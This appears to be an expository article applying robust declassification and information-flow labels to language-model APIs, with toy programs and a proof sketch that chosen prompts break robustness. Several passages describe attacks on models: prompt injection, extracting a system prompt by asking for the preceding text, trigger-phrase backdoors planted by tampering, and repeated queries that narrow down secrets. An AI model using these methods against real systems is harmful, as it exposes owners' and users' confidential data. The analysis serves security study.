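# Robust declassification when attackers choose a language model's prompts

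## Secrets, trust labels and a model behind an API

Robust declassification is a security condition for programs that deliberately release some of their secrets. An attacker may observe what such a program releases, but must not be able to change what they learn. Steve Zdancewic and Andrew Myers introduced the condition in 2001. It belongs to information-flow control, the branch of computer security that tracks data through a program and restricts what that data can influence.

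A language model behind an API is a program of this kind. The API is an interface through which outside customers send text and receive text back. The model's owner keeps its weights secret. These are the numbers, often billions of them, that training produced and that determine how the model responds to any input. The owner also sells responses that depend on those weights and lets customers decide what to ask.

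Restricting access to the weights file is not enough to keep the weights secret. In *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) describe an end-to-end goal, that an attacker who observes a system's output should be unable to infer its secret input. They point out that access control and encryption do not directly address this goal. Access control limits which programs may open the file, but the API server must be one of them, so secrecy then depends on what the server's output reveals.

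### Four labels

Information-flow control puts two labels on each piece of data. A confidentiality label marks who may learn the data, here either secret or public. An integrity label marks whether an attacker may have influenced the data (untrusted) or not (trusted). These ideas are decades old, and designers now rely on them for AI agents, which are programs in which a language model calls tools and acts on the results. *SPA* (2026) is one such agent design. It takes from Bell and LaPadula the rule that sensitive data must not reach unauthorised destinations, and from Biba the rule that untrustworthy data must not influence actions that need more trustworthy inputs.

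*Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness* (Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic) arranges the four combinations in a lattice, an ordering in which any two labels have a lowest label at or above both. Data may move only up the ordering, towards more secrecy and less trust. Public, trusted data is at the bottom, so it may flow anywhere, while secret, untrusted data is at the top and has to stay there. Neither of the other two labels is above the other, so data may not flow in either direction between a secret, trusted variable and a public, untrusted one.

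| Label | Can the attacker read it? | Can the attacker change it? | Example at an API |
|---|---|---|---|
| public, trusted | yes | no | the published price list |
| secret, trusted | no | no | the weights |
| public, untrusted | yes | yes | the attacker's own prompt |
| secret, untrusted | no | yes | a private mailbox that accepts mail from strangers |

Write-only access, as in the last row, is fairly common. *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm* (Kanniwadi and Myers, 2026) gives the example of a process that is allowed to write to a file but not read it, and can still blank out the first page.

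Which class a piece of data belongs to depends on the attacker. Myers and colleagues first specify what the attacker can read and affect, then sort the data into the four classes on that basis. For example, a contract that one customer uploads is secret if the attacker is another customer, but public if the attacker is the customer who uploaded it.

A value that a program computes from several inputs takes the lowest label at or above all of theirs, so it is secret if any input is secret and untrusted if any input is untrusted. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, build these four labels into a small programming language for agents and give each conversation with the model the combined label of everything the program has sent into it. A conversation that includes one private email and one stranger's web page therefore becomes secret and untrusted as a whole, along with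 every later response. This labelling is coarse, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists finer labelling as an open challenge, because a model processes its context (the text it is given when it answers) as one stream of tokens that may mix several sources.

### Noninterference

The simplest thing to want from a program with secrets is noninterference, the condition that secret inputs have no effect on public outputs. Write P(s, u) for what the public sees when a program P runs on a secret s and a public input u. Then P satisfies noninterference if

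P(s, u) = P(s′, u) for all s, s′ and u.

Someone who watches the output can then rule out no value of the secret. With p as a public variable, the program `p := u + 1` passes and `p := s` fails. *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* includes a less obvious failure, from earlier work by Denning:

`if s mod 2 = 0 then p := 0 else p := 1`

No line here assigns s to anything, yet the last bit of s ends up in p. Careful designers still miss implicit flows like this one. Garby and colleagues describe one in CaMeL, a leading defence for agents. CaMeL raises a variable's label when an assignment to it runs. If a secret stops the assignment from running, the variable keeps its public label, and its unchanged value reveals the secret.

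Language models usually sample their responses, so the same prompt can produce different answers, and the equality in the definition has to hold between probability distributions. Comparing only the sets of possible outputs is too weak. *Secure Typed Languages* (Meyers, 2019) shows this with a program that publishes either a secret number up to 100 or a random one from the same range. Any number in the range could come out whatever the secret is, but an attacker who runs the program many times will see the secret number more often than the others.

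Repetition also enlarges a leak that most versions of noninterference ignore. They disregard what an attacker learns from a program's failure to finish, on the grounds that it is about one bit per run. Garby and colleagues point out that CaMeL's tracking runs inside an ordinary retry loop that is itself untracked. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so an attacker who can trigger repeated attempts learns the whole secret one bit at a time.

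### Declassification and endorsement

Declassification is the deliberate relabelling of secret data as public:

`p := declassify(s)`

The operation copies the value of s into the variable p and changes only the label. Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, list some everyday reasons for it. Statisticians need the average salary from a secret database. A seller releases information once the buyer has paid. A login program has to report whether a password was right, and even from a failed login the attacker learns one string that is not the password.

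Endorsement works on the other label. It is the deliberate relabelling of untrusted data as trusted:

`t := endorse(u)`

Endorsement also leaves the value unchanged. Meyers gives an example from Battleship: when player A names a square, player B's program checks that the move is legal and then endorses it. The endorsement records that the rules require B to accept any legal square, not that A means well. In general, the justification for declassifying or endorsing a value comes from the application, and no automatic checker can supply it.

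A password checker needs both endorsement and declassification. In the version in *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* (Cecchetti, Myers and Arden, 2017), the program endorses the guess, compares it with the stored password and declassifies the yes or no. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes the same two operations as controlled exceptions for AI agents, which may have good reason to follow instructions in outside documentation or to release selected private information.

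Relabelling data breaks noninterference, which raises the question of what weaker guarantee remains. Garby and colleagues prove that in their language, relabelling along one dimension preserves the guarantee for the other, so an endorsement alone cannot make secret data public. Cecchetti and colleagues stress that once a program also declassifies, confidentiality depends on integrity. An attacker who can influence either the data being declassified or the decision to declassify it may use the declassification to extract secrets that the programmer meant to keep.

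### The API as a four-line program

Let w be the weights, u the user's prompt, and M(w, u) the output that a model with weights w computes for u. Stripped of billing and networking, the API is this program:

```
u := receive()          # public, untrusted
y := M(w, u)            # secret, untrusted
p := declassify(y)      # public, untrusted
send(p)
```

If the model samples its answers, M(w, u) is a probability distribution and y is one draw from it. In a longer conversation, u stands for the whole exchange so far, because each new response depends on all the earlier prompts and responses.

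The labels in the comments follow from the lattice. The weights are secret and trusted, and the prompt is public and untrusted. y is secret like the weights and untrusted like the prompt, which puts it at the top of the lattice. Only the third line lowers secrecy, and without it the server could not send anything back.

Noninterference would require M(w, u) to equal M(w′, u) for every prompt u and every two sets of weights w and w′. The owner could then replace the trained weights with random numbers without changing any output. Since training works by changing w, nobody would have a reason to train such a model. Every useful output depends on the secret weights, so the owner intends to release some information about them from the start.

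Researchers reached a similar conclusion about ordinary software long ago. Kanniwadi and Myers call noninterference "highly studied but too simple", and Meyers does not consider it the real security goal. But the API is a more extreme case than their examples, such as a password checker, which releases one yes or no per guess, computed by a line of code that a programmer can read. The API releases whole pages, which M computes using billions of numbers.

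The closest example in the literature to this program is a single line from Kanniwadi and Myers, `p := u * s`, where s is secret and u is untrusted and starts at zero. Someone who only watches p sees zero, but someone who can set u to 1 sees s. Their example is about programs in general, and they do not discuss language models, but replacing multiplication with M and s with w gives it the same form as the API.

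### What, who, where and when

If some release is intended, the owner needs a way of saying which. Sabelfeld and Sands sort the many proposals by four questions.

A policy can restrict *what* the program releases, *who* controls the release, *where* it happens and *when*. Restrictions on what is released might allow out only whether a number is odd or even, or at most four digits of a credit card number. They also include limits on the quantity of information. Where a release happens means between which labels, or at which lines of the code. Restrictions on when might allow a release only after the buyer has paid, for example, or only after more computation than any realistic attacker can perform. *Agent libOS* (2026), a runtime system for AI agents, still refers to this scheme and ties each release to one actor, one destination, one payload and one version of the policy, for a single use.

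An owner who answers one of these questions can still leave the others open. Sabelfeld and Sands show this with a credit card example. A shop's policy allows four digits of the card number to be released with each purchase, which is sensible for record-keeping, but it doesn't specify who picks the digits. An attacker who asks for different digits on different purchases soon has the full number, even though every release complied with the policy.

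Myers and colleagues say robustness mainly concerns the "who", and Sabelfeld and Sands agree. Robustness prevents attackers from influencing a release but doesn't limit how much is released. A server that published all of w to everybody, unasked, would therefore be robust but not secure. For this reason, Myers and colleagues present robustness as only one important part of a security policy.

For the API, "where" is the third line and "when" is each time a customer sends a request. "What" is harder to specify because the program releases M(w, u), which contains u. An owner cannot state what the server gives out without mentioning a value that the customer chooses, just as the shop could not say which four digits would appear. The customer therefore has a large influence on what the owner's program releases.

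### Two secrets and two attackers

The server often holds secrets besides the weights. Many services add other text to the model's context alongside the prompt, such as a system prompt (the operator's standing instructions) or private documents relevant to the question. If this text is d, the output becomes M(w, d + u), where d + u is the two texts joined.

Noninterference is hopeless for the weights w, but it can be a reasonable demand for d. A bank's assistant can be useful to one customer even if its answers to that customer do not depend at all on another customer's statements. The main theorem of Garby and colleagues guarantees noninterference of this sort for every program in their language, including agents that generate and run code, and they checked it by machine. They also built an agent in the language and tested it on the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection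 (attacks in which text that the model should only read works as an instruction). The agent resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 runs.

None of that protects the weights w. The labels apply to values that enter a conversation, and the model is taken as a given source of responses. The theorem compares runs that have different secret data but the same model, so it does not cover what the responses reveal about the weights. The weights of a large model are also too big to fit into a single response, unlike a system prompt.

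There are also two kinds of attacker. An outside user chooses u, reads p and has no other access. A stronger attacker has also tampered with the model or the server. Myers and colleagues allow for both kinds in ordinary software. Their attacker may be a regular user who gives a program unexpected inputs, or someone who controls an untrusted machine running part of a distributed program and can replace the code there.

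When the attacker is an outside user, only u is untrusted. Tampering makes M untrusted too, and perhaps w, but the third line of the program still declassifies whatever reaches it. An attacker who has altered the server's code could make it return part of w, disguised as harmless text, whenever the prompt contains a certain phrase. One who has altered only the weights could train the model to recite d when the phrase appears, but stealing w this way would be harder because a model does not ordinarily receive its own weights as input.

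## Robust declassification and what it requires

Myers and colleagues use a short program to show how an attacker can interfere with a release:

`if x then p := declassify(s)`

An attacker who can set x decides whether s becomes public, and one who can write to s, perhaps by getting another secret copied into it, can choose what is released. If the attacker can do neither, the program still releases s, but the attacker can't affect what it releases.

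Zdancewic and Myers (2001), in *Robust declassification*, stated this requirement for a state transition system, an abstract machine with only possible states and the steps between them. In that model, untrusted code and data appeared only during an active attack. This did not fit well with the problem that had inspired the idea, which was how to split one program across several computers when an attacker may control some of them. Part of such a program is untrusted even when no one is attacking.

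Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic moved the condition from abstract machines to programs in *Enforcing Robust Declassification* (full version 2006) and showed how a compiler could enforce it. Their definition makes untrusted code an explicit part of the program.

### Programs with holes

In the 2006 definition, the trusted code P is fixed except for holes, written [•], which the attacker fills with code. P[a] is P with its holes filled by attack a. In a program split across several computers, the holes are the parts that run on untrusted machines. If the attacker is a user who only supplies an input, one hole at the start is enough, and the attack is a single assignment such as `u := 5`.

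An attacker who could write `p := declassify(s)` into a hole could release the secret directly, so the definition considers only fair attacks. A fair attack may contain assignments, conditionals and loops, but it may read and write only public, untrusted variables and may not declassify. It can therefore reach a secret only by exploiting the trusted code. Myers and colleagues prove their results for a larger class of attacks, which may also write to secret, untrusted variables as long as nothing secret flows into a public one.

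Now write P[a](s) for the sequence of public values that an observer sees when P[a] runs on the secrets s, with the public starting values held fixed. P is robust if, for all secrets s and s′ and all fair attacks a and a′,

if P[a](s) = P[a](s′), then P[a′](s) = P[a′](s′).

Robustness requires that if attack a does not let the attacker tell s from s′, then no other attack does. Noninterference compares two runs of a program, while robustness, as Meyers points out, compares four, one for each combination of secret and attack.

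The multiplication example from Kanniwadi and Myers fails this test. Written with a hole and an explicit release, it is

`[•]; p := declassify(u * s)`

Suppose s is either 2 or 3. Under the attack `u := 0`, both values produce 0, so the attacker cannot tell them apart, but under `u := 1` they produce 2 and 3, so the attacker can. By contrast, `[•]; p := declassify(s)` passes because any two different secrets are distinguishable under every attack, so the "if" half of the condition never holds for them.

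Since a and a′ can swap places, every attack that lets the program finish must separate exactly the same pairs of secrets. One possible attack is to fill the holes with whatever the untrusted code would have done anyway and then watch, as a passive attacker does. An active attacker therefore learns no more than a passive one. This means a reviewer can look at what the program releases when nobody interferes and decide whether that is acceptable, without imagining every possible attack.

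The "if" half of the definition requires both runs to finish, while the "then" half counts a run that never finishes as matching any other run. The "if" half has this requirement because an incompetent attacker might fill a hole with an infinite loop and see nothing. If that counted as failing to tell s from s′, no attack would be allowed to tell any two secrets apart, and robustness would be the same as noninterference.

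It might seem simpler to compare each attack with an empty hole. Myers and colleagues show why this would not work with the following program, in which `skip` is a command that does nothing:

`x := 1; [•]; while x > 0 do skip; if x = 0 then p := declassify(s)`

With an empty hole, the program loops forever, which leaves nothing to compare. But an attacker who sets x to 0 receives s, and one who sets it to −1 receives nothing. The definition compares all pairs of attacks, including these two, so it correctly classifies the program as not robust.

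### The typing rule

Checking the definition directly would require running a program on every pair of secrets under every pair of attacks. Myers and colleagues instead provide a type system, a set of rules that a compiler applies to a program's text before the program runs.

Every variable has a label, and so does every point in the program. The label of a program point, called pc for "program counter", combines the labels of everything that determined whether execution would get there. Inside the branch of `if x then ...`, for example, pc is at least as secret and at least as untrusted as x. The compiler accepts `p := declassify(e)` only if

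e is trusted and pc is trusted.

The requirement on e prevents the attacker from changing what the program releases, and the requirement on pc prevents them from changing whether the release happens. The usual rules for assignments still apply, so a release to a public variable cannot appear inside a branch that depends on a secret. Similarly, pc must be public wherever there is a hole, because otherwise the attacker could learn a secret by noticing whether their code ran.

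An earlier type system, from Zdancewic (2003), in *A Type System for Robust Declassification*, checked pc but not e. Myers and colleagues give an example of what it missed:

`[•]; if x then y := s1 else y := s2; p := declassify(y)`

Here x is secret and untrusted, so the attacker can set it but not read it. The declassification comes after the branch and happens whatever x is, so pc is trusted at that point. But x determines which of the two secrets is in y, so the attacker chooses which one to publish. The 2006 rule rejects the program because y is untrusted, since it depends on x.

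The main theorem is that every program these rules accept is robust. The proof works through the program piece by piece. Attack code cannot write to trusted variables, and the rules prevent untrusted values from flowing into them, so trusted data takes the same values under every attack. Each declassified value and the decision to declassify it depend only on trusted data, so the releases are also the same under every attack. The rest of the program satisfies noninterference and reveals nothing more.

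The theorem does not guarantee that every robust program will pass. A compiler that follows these rules rejects some harmless programs, and a programmer then has to rewrite them or justify an exception.

### Laundering a secret through a password check

The password checker in the 2006 paper works like the one in UNIX. The system stores a hash of the password rather than the password itself. The hash is computed from the password and a public string called the salt, and is designed to be hard to reverse. When someone tries to log in, the program hashes their guess with the same salt, declassifies the result and compares it with the stored hash.

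Suppose the same system holds another secret, x, which has nothing to do with passwords. An attacker gets the program to hash x and use the result in place of the stored password hash. They then supply a guess y:

`[•]; match(hash(x, 0), 0, y); if matched then z := 1 else z := 0`

The two zeros are the salt. The public variable z is now 1 if x equals y and 0 otherwise. The checker correctly reports whether a guess matches a hash, but the hash is of a secret that nobody meant to expose. If x is a four-digit PIN, the attacker needs at most 10,000 guesses to find it.

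This program violates the definition of robustness. Suppose x is either 2 or 3. If the attacker guesses 0, the answer is no in both cases, but if they guess 2, the answer is yes in one case and no in the other. The type system also rejects the program, because the program hashes and declassifies y, which is untrusted.

Myers calls this laundering secrets via declassification and describes a version in which the attacker overwrites the stored password with the secret they want to test. Some other policies allow this attack. Intransitive noninterference, for instance, lets secrets become public only by passing through designated trusted components. Myers and colleagues point out that the laundering program satisfies a typical version of this policy. The secret leaves through an approved component, and the policy does not restrict who chooses that component's input.

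The typing rule also rejects legitimate login pages, because a stranger's password guess is untrusted. Endorsing the guess lets the program pass the rule, but the program then satisfies only a weaker condition, qualified robustness.

### A definition that works for servers

The 2006 treatment of unfinished runs has a serious consequence. If a program never finishes, the "if" half of the definition is never true, and the program counts as robust whatever it releases along the way. Servers are meant to run indefinitely. This one publishes s to the first customer who sets u to 1, and it satisfies the 2006 definition:

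`while true do ([•]; p := declassify(u * s))`

Askarov and Myers (2011), in *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity*, gave this as one of two reasons for replacing the definition. The other was that they considered its treatment of endorsement somewhat ad hoc. Their replacement is based on what the attacker has learned after each public event, meaning each assignment to a public variable, so it applies even before a program ends.

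Attacker knowledge is the set of secrets compatible with everything the attacker has observed. A smaller set means the attacker knows more. The set never grows as the program runs, and a public event that shrinks it is a release event.

For example, let h be a secret number that happens to be 7, and consider

`[•]; p := u > h`

Askarov and Myers leave out the word `declassify` in examples like this one and treat any assignment of secret information to a public variable as a possible release. An attacker who sets u to 10 sees p become 1 and learns that h is below 10. Setting u to 5 gives 0 and reveals that h is at least 5. Setting u to 0 also gives 0, but reveals only that h is at least 0. An attacker can therefore learn different things from two attacks that produce the same output.

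They also redefine fair attacks in terms of knowledge. The 2006 definition listed the commands an attacker could use. The new one allows any code that doesn't change trusted variables, as long as the attacker learns nothing from it beyond the fact that execution reached the hole. In `if h > 0 then [•]`, the attack `p := (h > 0)` is fair, because anyone whose code runs there already knows that h is positive. The attack `p := h` is unfair because it also reveals the value of h.

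Two attacks are similar if they lead to the same releases in the same order, with nothing learned in between. Similarity compares the published values rather than the knowledge sets, so with h = 7, setting u to 0 and setting it to 5 are similar attacks on the program above. Setting u to 10 is not similar to either.

Attacker control is the set of all attacks similar to the actual one, judged by the events so far. The name is a little confusing, because a larger set means the attacker has had less influence. The set contains every possible attack as long as the attacker's choice of attack has made no difference to events, and it shrinks each time the choice does.

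Release control is the part of that set that still matters for future releases. It contains the attacks that cause another release event or let the program finish. If the attacker can tell that a program has hung, release control also contains attacks that make the program hang in a way that reveals something. It leaves out attacks that only hang the program and from which the attacker learns nothing.

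A program is robust under the new definition if, at every release event,

release control just before the event ⊆ attacker control just after it.

Every attack that could still have led to a release, or to the end of the program, must lead to this same release.

If the attacker sets u to 5 in the program `[•]; p := u < h`, again with h = 7, the program publishes 1. Just before that, release control contains every attack that reaches the assignment, including `u := 9`. Just afterwards, attacker control contains only the attacks that set u below 7, since the others would have published 0. The attack `u := 9` is in the first set but not in the second, so the program is not robust.

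Now suppose the program releases h first:

`[•]; p := h; q := u < h`

The first assignment publishes 7 under every attack that reaches it, so the two sets agree. The attacker then knows h and can work out whether u is less than 7. The second assignment therefore reveals nothing new to them, so it isn't a release event, the condition doesn't apply to it, and the program is robust.

Reversing the two assignments makes the program fail at the first one, for the same reason as before. The 2006 definition cannot distinguish the two orders because it compares complete runs, and by the end of either run the attacker knows h whatever they did. But a program on a server may never end, and an attacker who disconnects after the first answer has chosen exactly what they learned.

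The table compares the two definitions on these programs and three others from the paper. The hole comes first in each program. The last column is for an attacker who can tell when a program has hung.

| Program after the hole | 2006 definition | 2011 definition |
|---|---|---|
| `p := u < h` | not robust | not robust |
| `p := h; q := u < h` | robust | robust |
| `p := u < h; q := h` | robust | not robust |
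| `if u > 0 then p := h` | not robust | not robust |
| `while u > 0 do skip; p := h` | robust | robust |
| `while u > h do skip; p := 1` | robust | not robust |

In the fourth program, the attacker decides whether the program releases h. In the fifth, the attacker can only make the program hang before it releases anything. Askarov and Myers call this a pure availability attack, and their definition ignores it because the attacker gains no information from it. In the last program, hanging reveals that h is less than u, which the attacker chose.

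Observers cannot always tell whether a program has hung or is just slow, so Askarov and Myers also give a more lenient definition that ignores what hanging reveals. The last program is robust under this definition. They keep much the same type system as in 2006 and prove that it guarantees robustness in this lenient sense, now also for programs that run forever.

The type system is still stricter than the definition. It requires every variable in a declassified expression to be trusted, so it rejects `p := declassify(h); q := declassify(u < h)` for containing the untrusted u, even though the attacker learns nothing new from the second release. To determine that the program is harmless, a checker would have to track what the attacker already knows, but these rules track only labels.

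### Several parties who distrust each other

All of these definitions assume a single attacker with fixed powers. In many systems, though, each participant regards the others as possible attackers. In *Decentralized Robustness*, Chong and Myers give the example of a series of ten sealed-bid auctions. In each one, Alice and Bob submit secret bids to an auctioneer, who waits until both bids are in, then makes them public and announces the winner.

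Alice has reason to worry that Bob could get her bid declassified before he submits his own, which would let him win every time with the lowest bid that beats hers. If he could alter the variable that holds her bid, he might also get the program to publish her credit card number instead, or her bid in the next auction. Bob has the same worries about Alice, and both may worry about the auctioneer.

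Chong and Myers call a program robust against all attackers if, for every pair of participants, it is robust when one attacks with the powers the other believes the attacker has. They express these beliefs using the decentralized label model, in which a label records who may read a piece of data and who may have influenced it, according to each participant. For instance, the label on Alice's bid records that she lets only the auctioneer read it, and that she and Bob both accept that only the auctioneer could have influenced it.

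The condition on each declassification naturally extends the 2006 rule. If the release lets someone read data that they could not read before, that person must not have been able to influence either the data or the decision to release it. A compiler has trouble checking this directly because participants can delegate authority to one another while the program runs. The compiler cannot prove that Bob has no influence if somebody might later authorise him to act for the auctioneer.

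Chong and Myers solve this by checking instead that anyone who can read the result and could have influenced the release could already read the original data. The compiler can confirm this from the labels alone, even if it knows only some of the delegations. Alice's auction passes because only the auctioneer could have influenced the release of her bid, and the auctioneer could read the bid from the start. Chong and Myers prove that a program that passes this check throughout is robust against all attackers, and they added the rules to Jif, a version of Java with information-flow labels.

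By the same rule, a customer may influence which parts of their own uploaded contract a server sends them, but not which parts of another customer's contract, because that would let them read something they could not read before.

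## Why a model that answers chosen prompts violates the definition

The 2006 type system rejects the API program at its third line because a program may declassify only trusted values, and y depends on the customer's prompt. But the type system also rejects some robust programs, so we have to apply the definition itself to determine whether the API program is robust.

The argument has three premises:

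- Prompts are untrusted, because the attacker may be a customer and customers write their own prompts.
- Outputs are public, because the server sends them to that customer.
- Different prompts can reveal different facts about the weights. More precisely, there are two possible sets of weights that give the same output for one prompt but different outputs for another.

In a robust program, if an attacker cannot distinguish two secrets with one attack, they cannot distinguish them with any other. The API is not robust, because an attacker can distinguish the two sets of weights with one prompt but not with another.

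Only the premise about different facts depends on the model, and it is easy to satisfy. If the owner retrains a model to correct its answer to one history question, and it still answers 2 + 2 with 4, the old and new weights are the kind of pair the argument requires.

A model's answer can reveal information about its weights even when it tells the customer nothing new about the world. A customer who already knows the capital of France and gets the answer "Paris" learns nothing about France, but can rule out every set of weights that would have produced a different answer.

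Myers and colleagues give a small program with the same problem, in which a customer buys one of two pieces of secret information:

`[•]; if x = 1 then z := declassify(y1) else z := declassify(y2)`

The buyer sets x, which determines the item they receive. The program violates robustness because different choices release different information, yet Myers and colleagues say it can reasonably be considered secure, since the seller doesn't care which item the buyer takes as long as they pay. The API is like a shop with one item for every possible prompt, so violating robustness doesn't prove that the owner has lost anything valuable.

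But the owner loses a convenient way of checking the program. A reviewer can check a robust program by looking only at what it releases when nobody interferes. An API releases nothing until somebody sends a prompt, so it has no undisturbed run to look at. A reviewer could read the answers to ten thousand ordinary prompts and still have no guarantee about what an unusual prompt would reveal.

### Every prompt sorts the possible weights

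For a model that always finishes and always gives the same answer to the same prompt, the definition reduces to a simple test. The test uses an idea from Sabelfeld and Sands, who model an attacker's knowledge by grouping together the possible values of a secret that the attacker cannot tell apart. If a program releases nothing, all the values are in one group. If it releases whether a secret number is odd or even, there are two groups, and if it releases the number itself, every value has its own group.

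A prompt sorts weights in the same way. Two sets of weights are in the same group if they give the same output. Suppose, for illustration, that there are only three possible sets of weights, A, B and C:

| Prompt | A | B | C | Groups |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| What is 2 + 2? | 4 | 4 | 4 | A, B and C together |
| Who wrote *Middlemarch*? | George Eliot | George Eliot | Jane Austen | A and B together; C alone |
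| Name a prime above 10. | 11 | 13 | 13 | A alone; B and C together |

An attacker who asks the question about *Middlemarch* can identify C but cannot tell A from B. Asking for a prime distinguishes A from B but not B from C, so asking both questions always lets the attacker tell which of the three the server is using.

The API is robust exactly when every prompt sorts the possible weights into the same groups. To see why, consider what an attack on a single request can do. The only hole comes before the server reads u, and attack code can use only public, untrusted variables. However complicated the code is, it either runs forever or leaves some particular prompt in u. Attacks that run forever cannot violate the 2006 definition, because it makes an exception for unfinished runs. For the rest, the definition says that for all prompts u and u′ and all weights w and w′,

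if M(w, u) = M(w′, u), then M(w, u′) = M(w′, u′).

Weights that share a group under u must therefore share a group under u′. Since u and u′ can swap places, the reverse is also true, so the two groupings are identical. Conversely, if all the groupings are identical, the condition holds. This result comes from applying the published definition to the API. Myers and colleagues do not state it as a theorem.

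Askarov and Myers's 2011 definition is stricter. In the program `[•]; p := h + u`, the attacker knows u and can subtract it from p, so they learn h exactly, whichever u they chose. Each value of h is in its own group for every u, so the program satisfies the 2006 definition. But the 2011 definition compares the published values, which change with u, so taken literally it rejects the program. For the API, it would require that whenever an answer reveals something about the weights, every other prompt would have produced the same answer. A model that revealed one fixed fact, but in the language of the prompt, would fail.

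### What an attacker gains by asking again

One answer may reveal very little. In the threshold program `p := u > h`, p is always 0 or 1, so a single query gives the attacker at most one bit of information on average. But if the program runs on a server, the attacker can ask again and choose each threshold using the earlier answers. Suppose h is a four-bit number, which means it is between 0 and 15, and it happens to be 7. Four queries are enough to find it:

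| Attacker sets u to | Server publishes | Values of h still possible |
|---|---|---|
| 8 | 1 | 0 to 7 |
| 4 | 0 | 4 to 7 |
| 6 | 0 | 6 or 7 |
| 7 | 0 | 7 |

This is binary search. Each answer halves the number of possible secrets, so n queries recover an n-bit secret. No method can guarantee success with fewer, because n − 1 one-bit answers have only 2ⁿ⁻¹ combinations, too few to distinguish 2ⁿ secrets.

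Much of the attacker's power comes from reacting to earlier answers. An attacker who had to choose all the thresholds in advance would need every one from 1 to 15, since, for instance, only a threshold of 7 separates 6 from 7. Finding a 64-bit number takes 64 queries if the attacker can react to earlier answers and about 18 billion billion if not.

How quickly a secret leaks also depends on the kind of question asked. Sabelfeld and Sands point out that a function that only tests whether a secret equals a chosen value can eventually reveal the whole secret, but much more slowly than one that releases it directly. Finding the four-bit number this way could take 15 guesses.

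Sabelfeld and Myers describe a similar attack on an electronic wallet in *A Model for Delimited Information Release*. The wallet program declassifies whether a secret balance covers the price of an item and, if it does, subtracts the price. The attack tries prices that are powers of two, starting with the largest, until the amount spent equals the original balance. This attack changes the secret, whereas API customers can't change the weights, but an attacker can get the same information from a fixed secret by changing the threshold instead.

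Even honest use of the wallet has this problem. Banerjee, Naumann and Rosenberg observe in *Expressive Declassification Policies and Modular Static Enforcement* that enough permitted transactions could reveal the entire balance. They suggest defining policies for a whole session but leave that to future work.

Customers of a language model aren't given a threshold test on its weights, so binary search does not show how many prompts it would take to steal the model. Prompts also can't reveal exactly which weights file the owner has. If the owner reorders the units in one layer of a neural network and moves their connections with them, the file changes but the outputs stay the same, so no prompt can distinguish the two files. At most, an attacker can learn which sets of weights give the same output as the original for every prompt, though any of those sets would be as useful as the original.

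### Attempts to make the API robust

An owner can make the API robust by having it ignore either the weights or the prompt. If the server sends everyone the same fixed sentence, all possible weights are in one group. If it always sends the model's score on a standard exam, the groups are the same whatever the customer asks. However, neither server would answer customers' questions. Limiting customers to a list of approved prompts makes the API robust only if all the prompts on the list sort the weights into the same groups.

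Publishing the weights also makes the API robust. The API then resembles the robust program that releases h before answering a question about it. Anyone who has the weights can compute M(w, u), so the API's answers reveal nothing more about w. Robustness does not measure how much a program releases, so a company that gives its weights away satisfies it, even though a company that keeps its weights secret and answers questions does not.

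This loophole also covers weights that the attacker could not feasibly compute, because the definition of attacker knowledge sets no limit on computation. Suppose the owner publishes only a hash of the weights, and no two possible sets of weights have the same hash. The hash then identifies the weights, so the 2011 definition treats them as already known and every later answer as harmless, even though nobody could work backwards from the hash in practice. Sabelfeld and Sands describe a similar flaw in delimited release, a policy that lets a program reveal only the values of expressions marked in its code. The policy accepts a program that declassifies a password's hash and then publishes the password itself, provided that no other password has the same hash.

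Publishing the weights also doesn't protect secrets in the model's context. If d is a confidential system prompt, M(w, d + u) can still depend on d. A request to repeat the preceding text might reveal all of d, while a question about arithmetic might reveal none of it. The server would then be robust for w but not for d.

The API still violates the definition if it samples its answers randomly. As with noninterference, we compare probability distributions instead of outputs, so two sets of weights are in the same group under a prompt if each possible answer is as likely from one as from the other. Sabelfeld and Sands mention that they had already extended the grouping model to probabilistic systems.

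Different prompts can still produce different groupings. A language model normally first looks up a row of numbers for each token in the prompt. Suppose the model uses these rows only to read its input, and two sets of weights differ only in the row for the token "zebra". If a prompt doesn't contain that token, both sets give exactly the same probabilities for the next token. If it does, the probabilities will generally differ. An API that returns one sampled token per request therefore fails the test.

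Sampling slows the attacker down. If one set of weights answers "yes" 50% of the time and another 51%, the attacker needs around 40,000 samples to tell them apart with about 98% reliability. The number of samples needed doesn't affect the test's result, which depends only on whether the probabilities are equal.

The owner could also declare all customers trusted. Their prompts would then be trusted too, and the program would pass because nobody would count as an attacker. Askarov and Myers have an example that shows the trouble with this. A service holds new data that it must not release before a certain time:

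`if request_time >= embargo_time then return declassify(new_data) else return old_data`

The requester supplies `request_time`. The type system allows the programmer to label it as trusted, but the requester can still give a time later than the real one and get the data early. The label describes how the owner expects requesters to behave but doesn't constrain them. That expectation might be reasonable for a tool that only a few of the owner's employees can use, but a public API accepts prompts from strangers.

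### Weights that are both secret and code

Formally, the weights w are a secret like any other, and the software that runs the model is an ordinary program that combines them with numbers derived from the prompt. But how the API responds to a prompt depends mostly on w. The owner could turn a translator into a chess player by replacing the weights, without changing the software. The weights are therefore also a kind of code that interprets the prompt.

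The classical definitions assume that the code is known and only the data is secret. Banerjee and colleagues state explicitly that everyone can read the running code and nobody can alter it. Customers who use a model through an API cannot read its weights. The owner can, but reading billions of weights does little to help predict what the model will output for a prompt that nobody has tried.

This matters because reviewers rely on the code to learn what a program releases. Delimited release makes programmers state this explicitly, which Sabelfeld and Myers consider a strength. Anyone who reads `declassify(parity(h))` knows that the program reveals whether h is odd or even. The equivalent line at the API is `declassify(M(w, u))`, which permits the server to release whatever the model outputs. Each request on its own satisfies delimited release automatically, because the program reveals nothing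 except the marked expression, but that does not help the owner judge whether the output is acceptable.

The rule that attack code may not read secrets is also less of a restriction than it seems. Consider this program, in which u is program text and `run` executes it with access to the secret s:

`[•]; p := declassify(run(u, s))`

The attacker only has to set u to the text of a short program that returns s. This is a fair attack because it only writes a public string. The trusted code then reads the secret for the attacker. A prompt can expose the model's context in much the same way, since a model that follows instructions may follow one to repeat its system prompt. The comparison is looser for the weights, which the model doesn't have as text.

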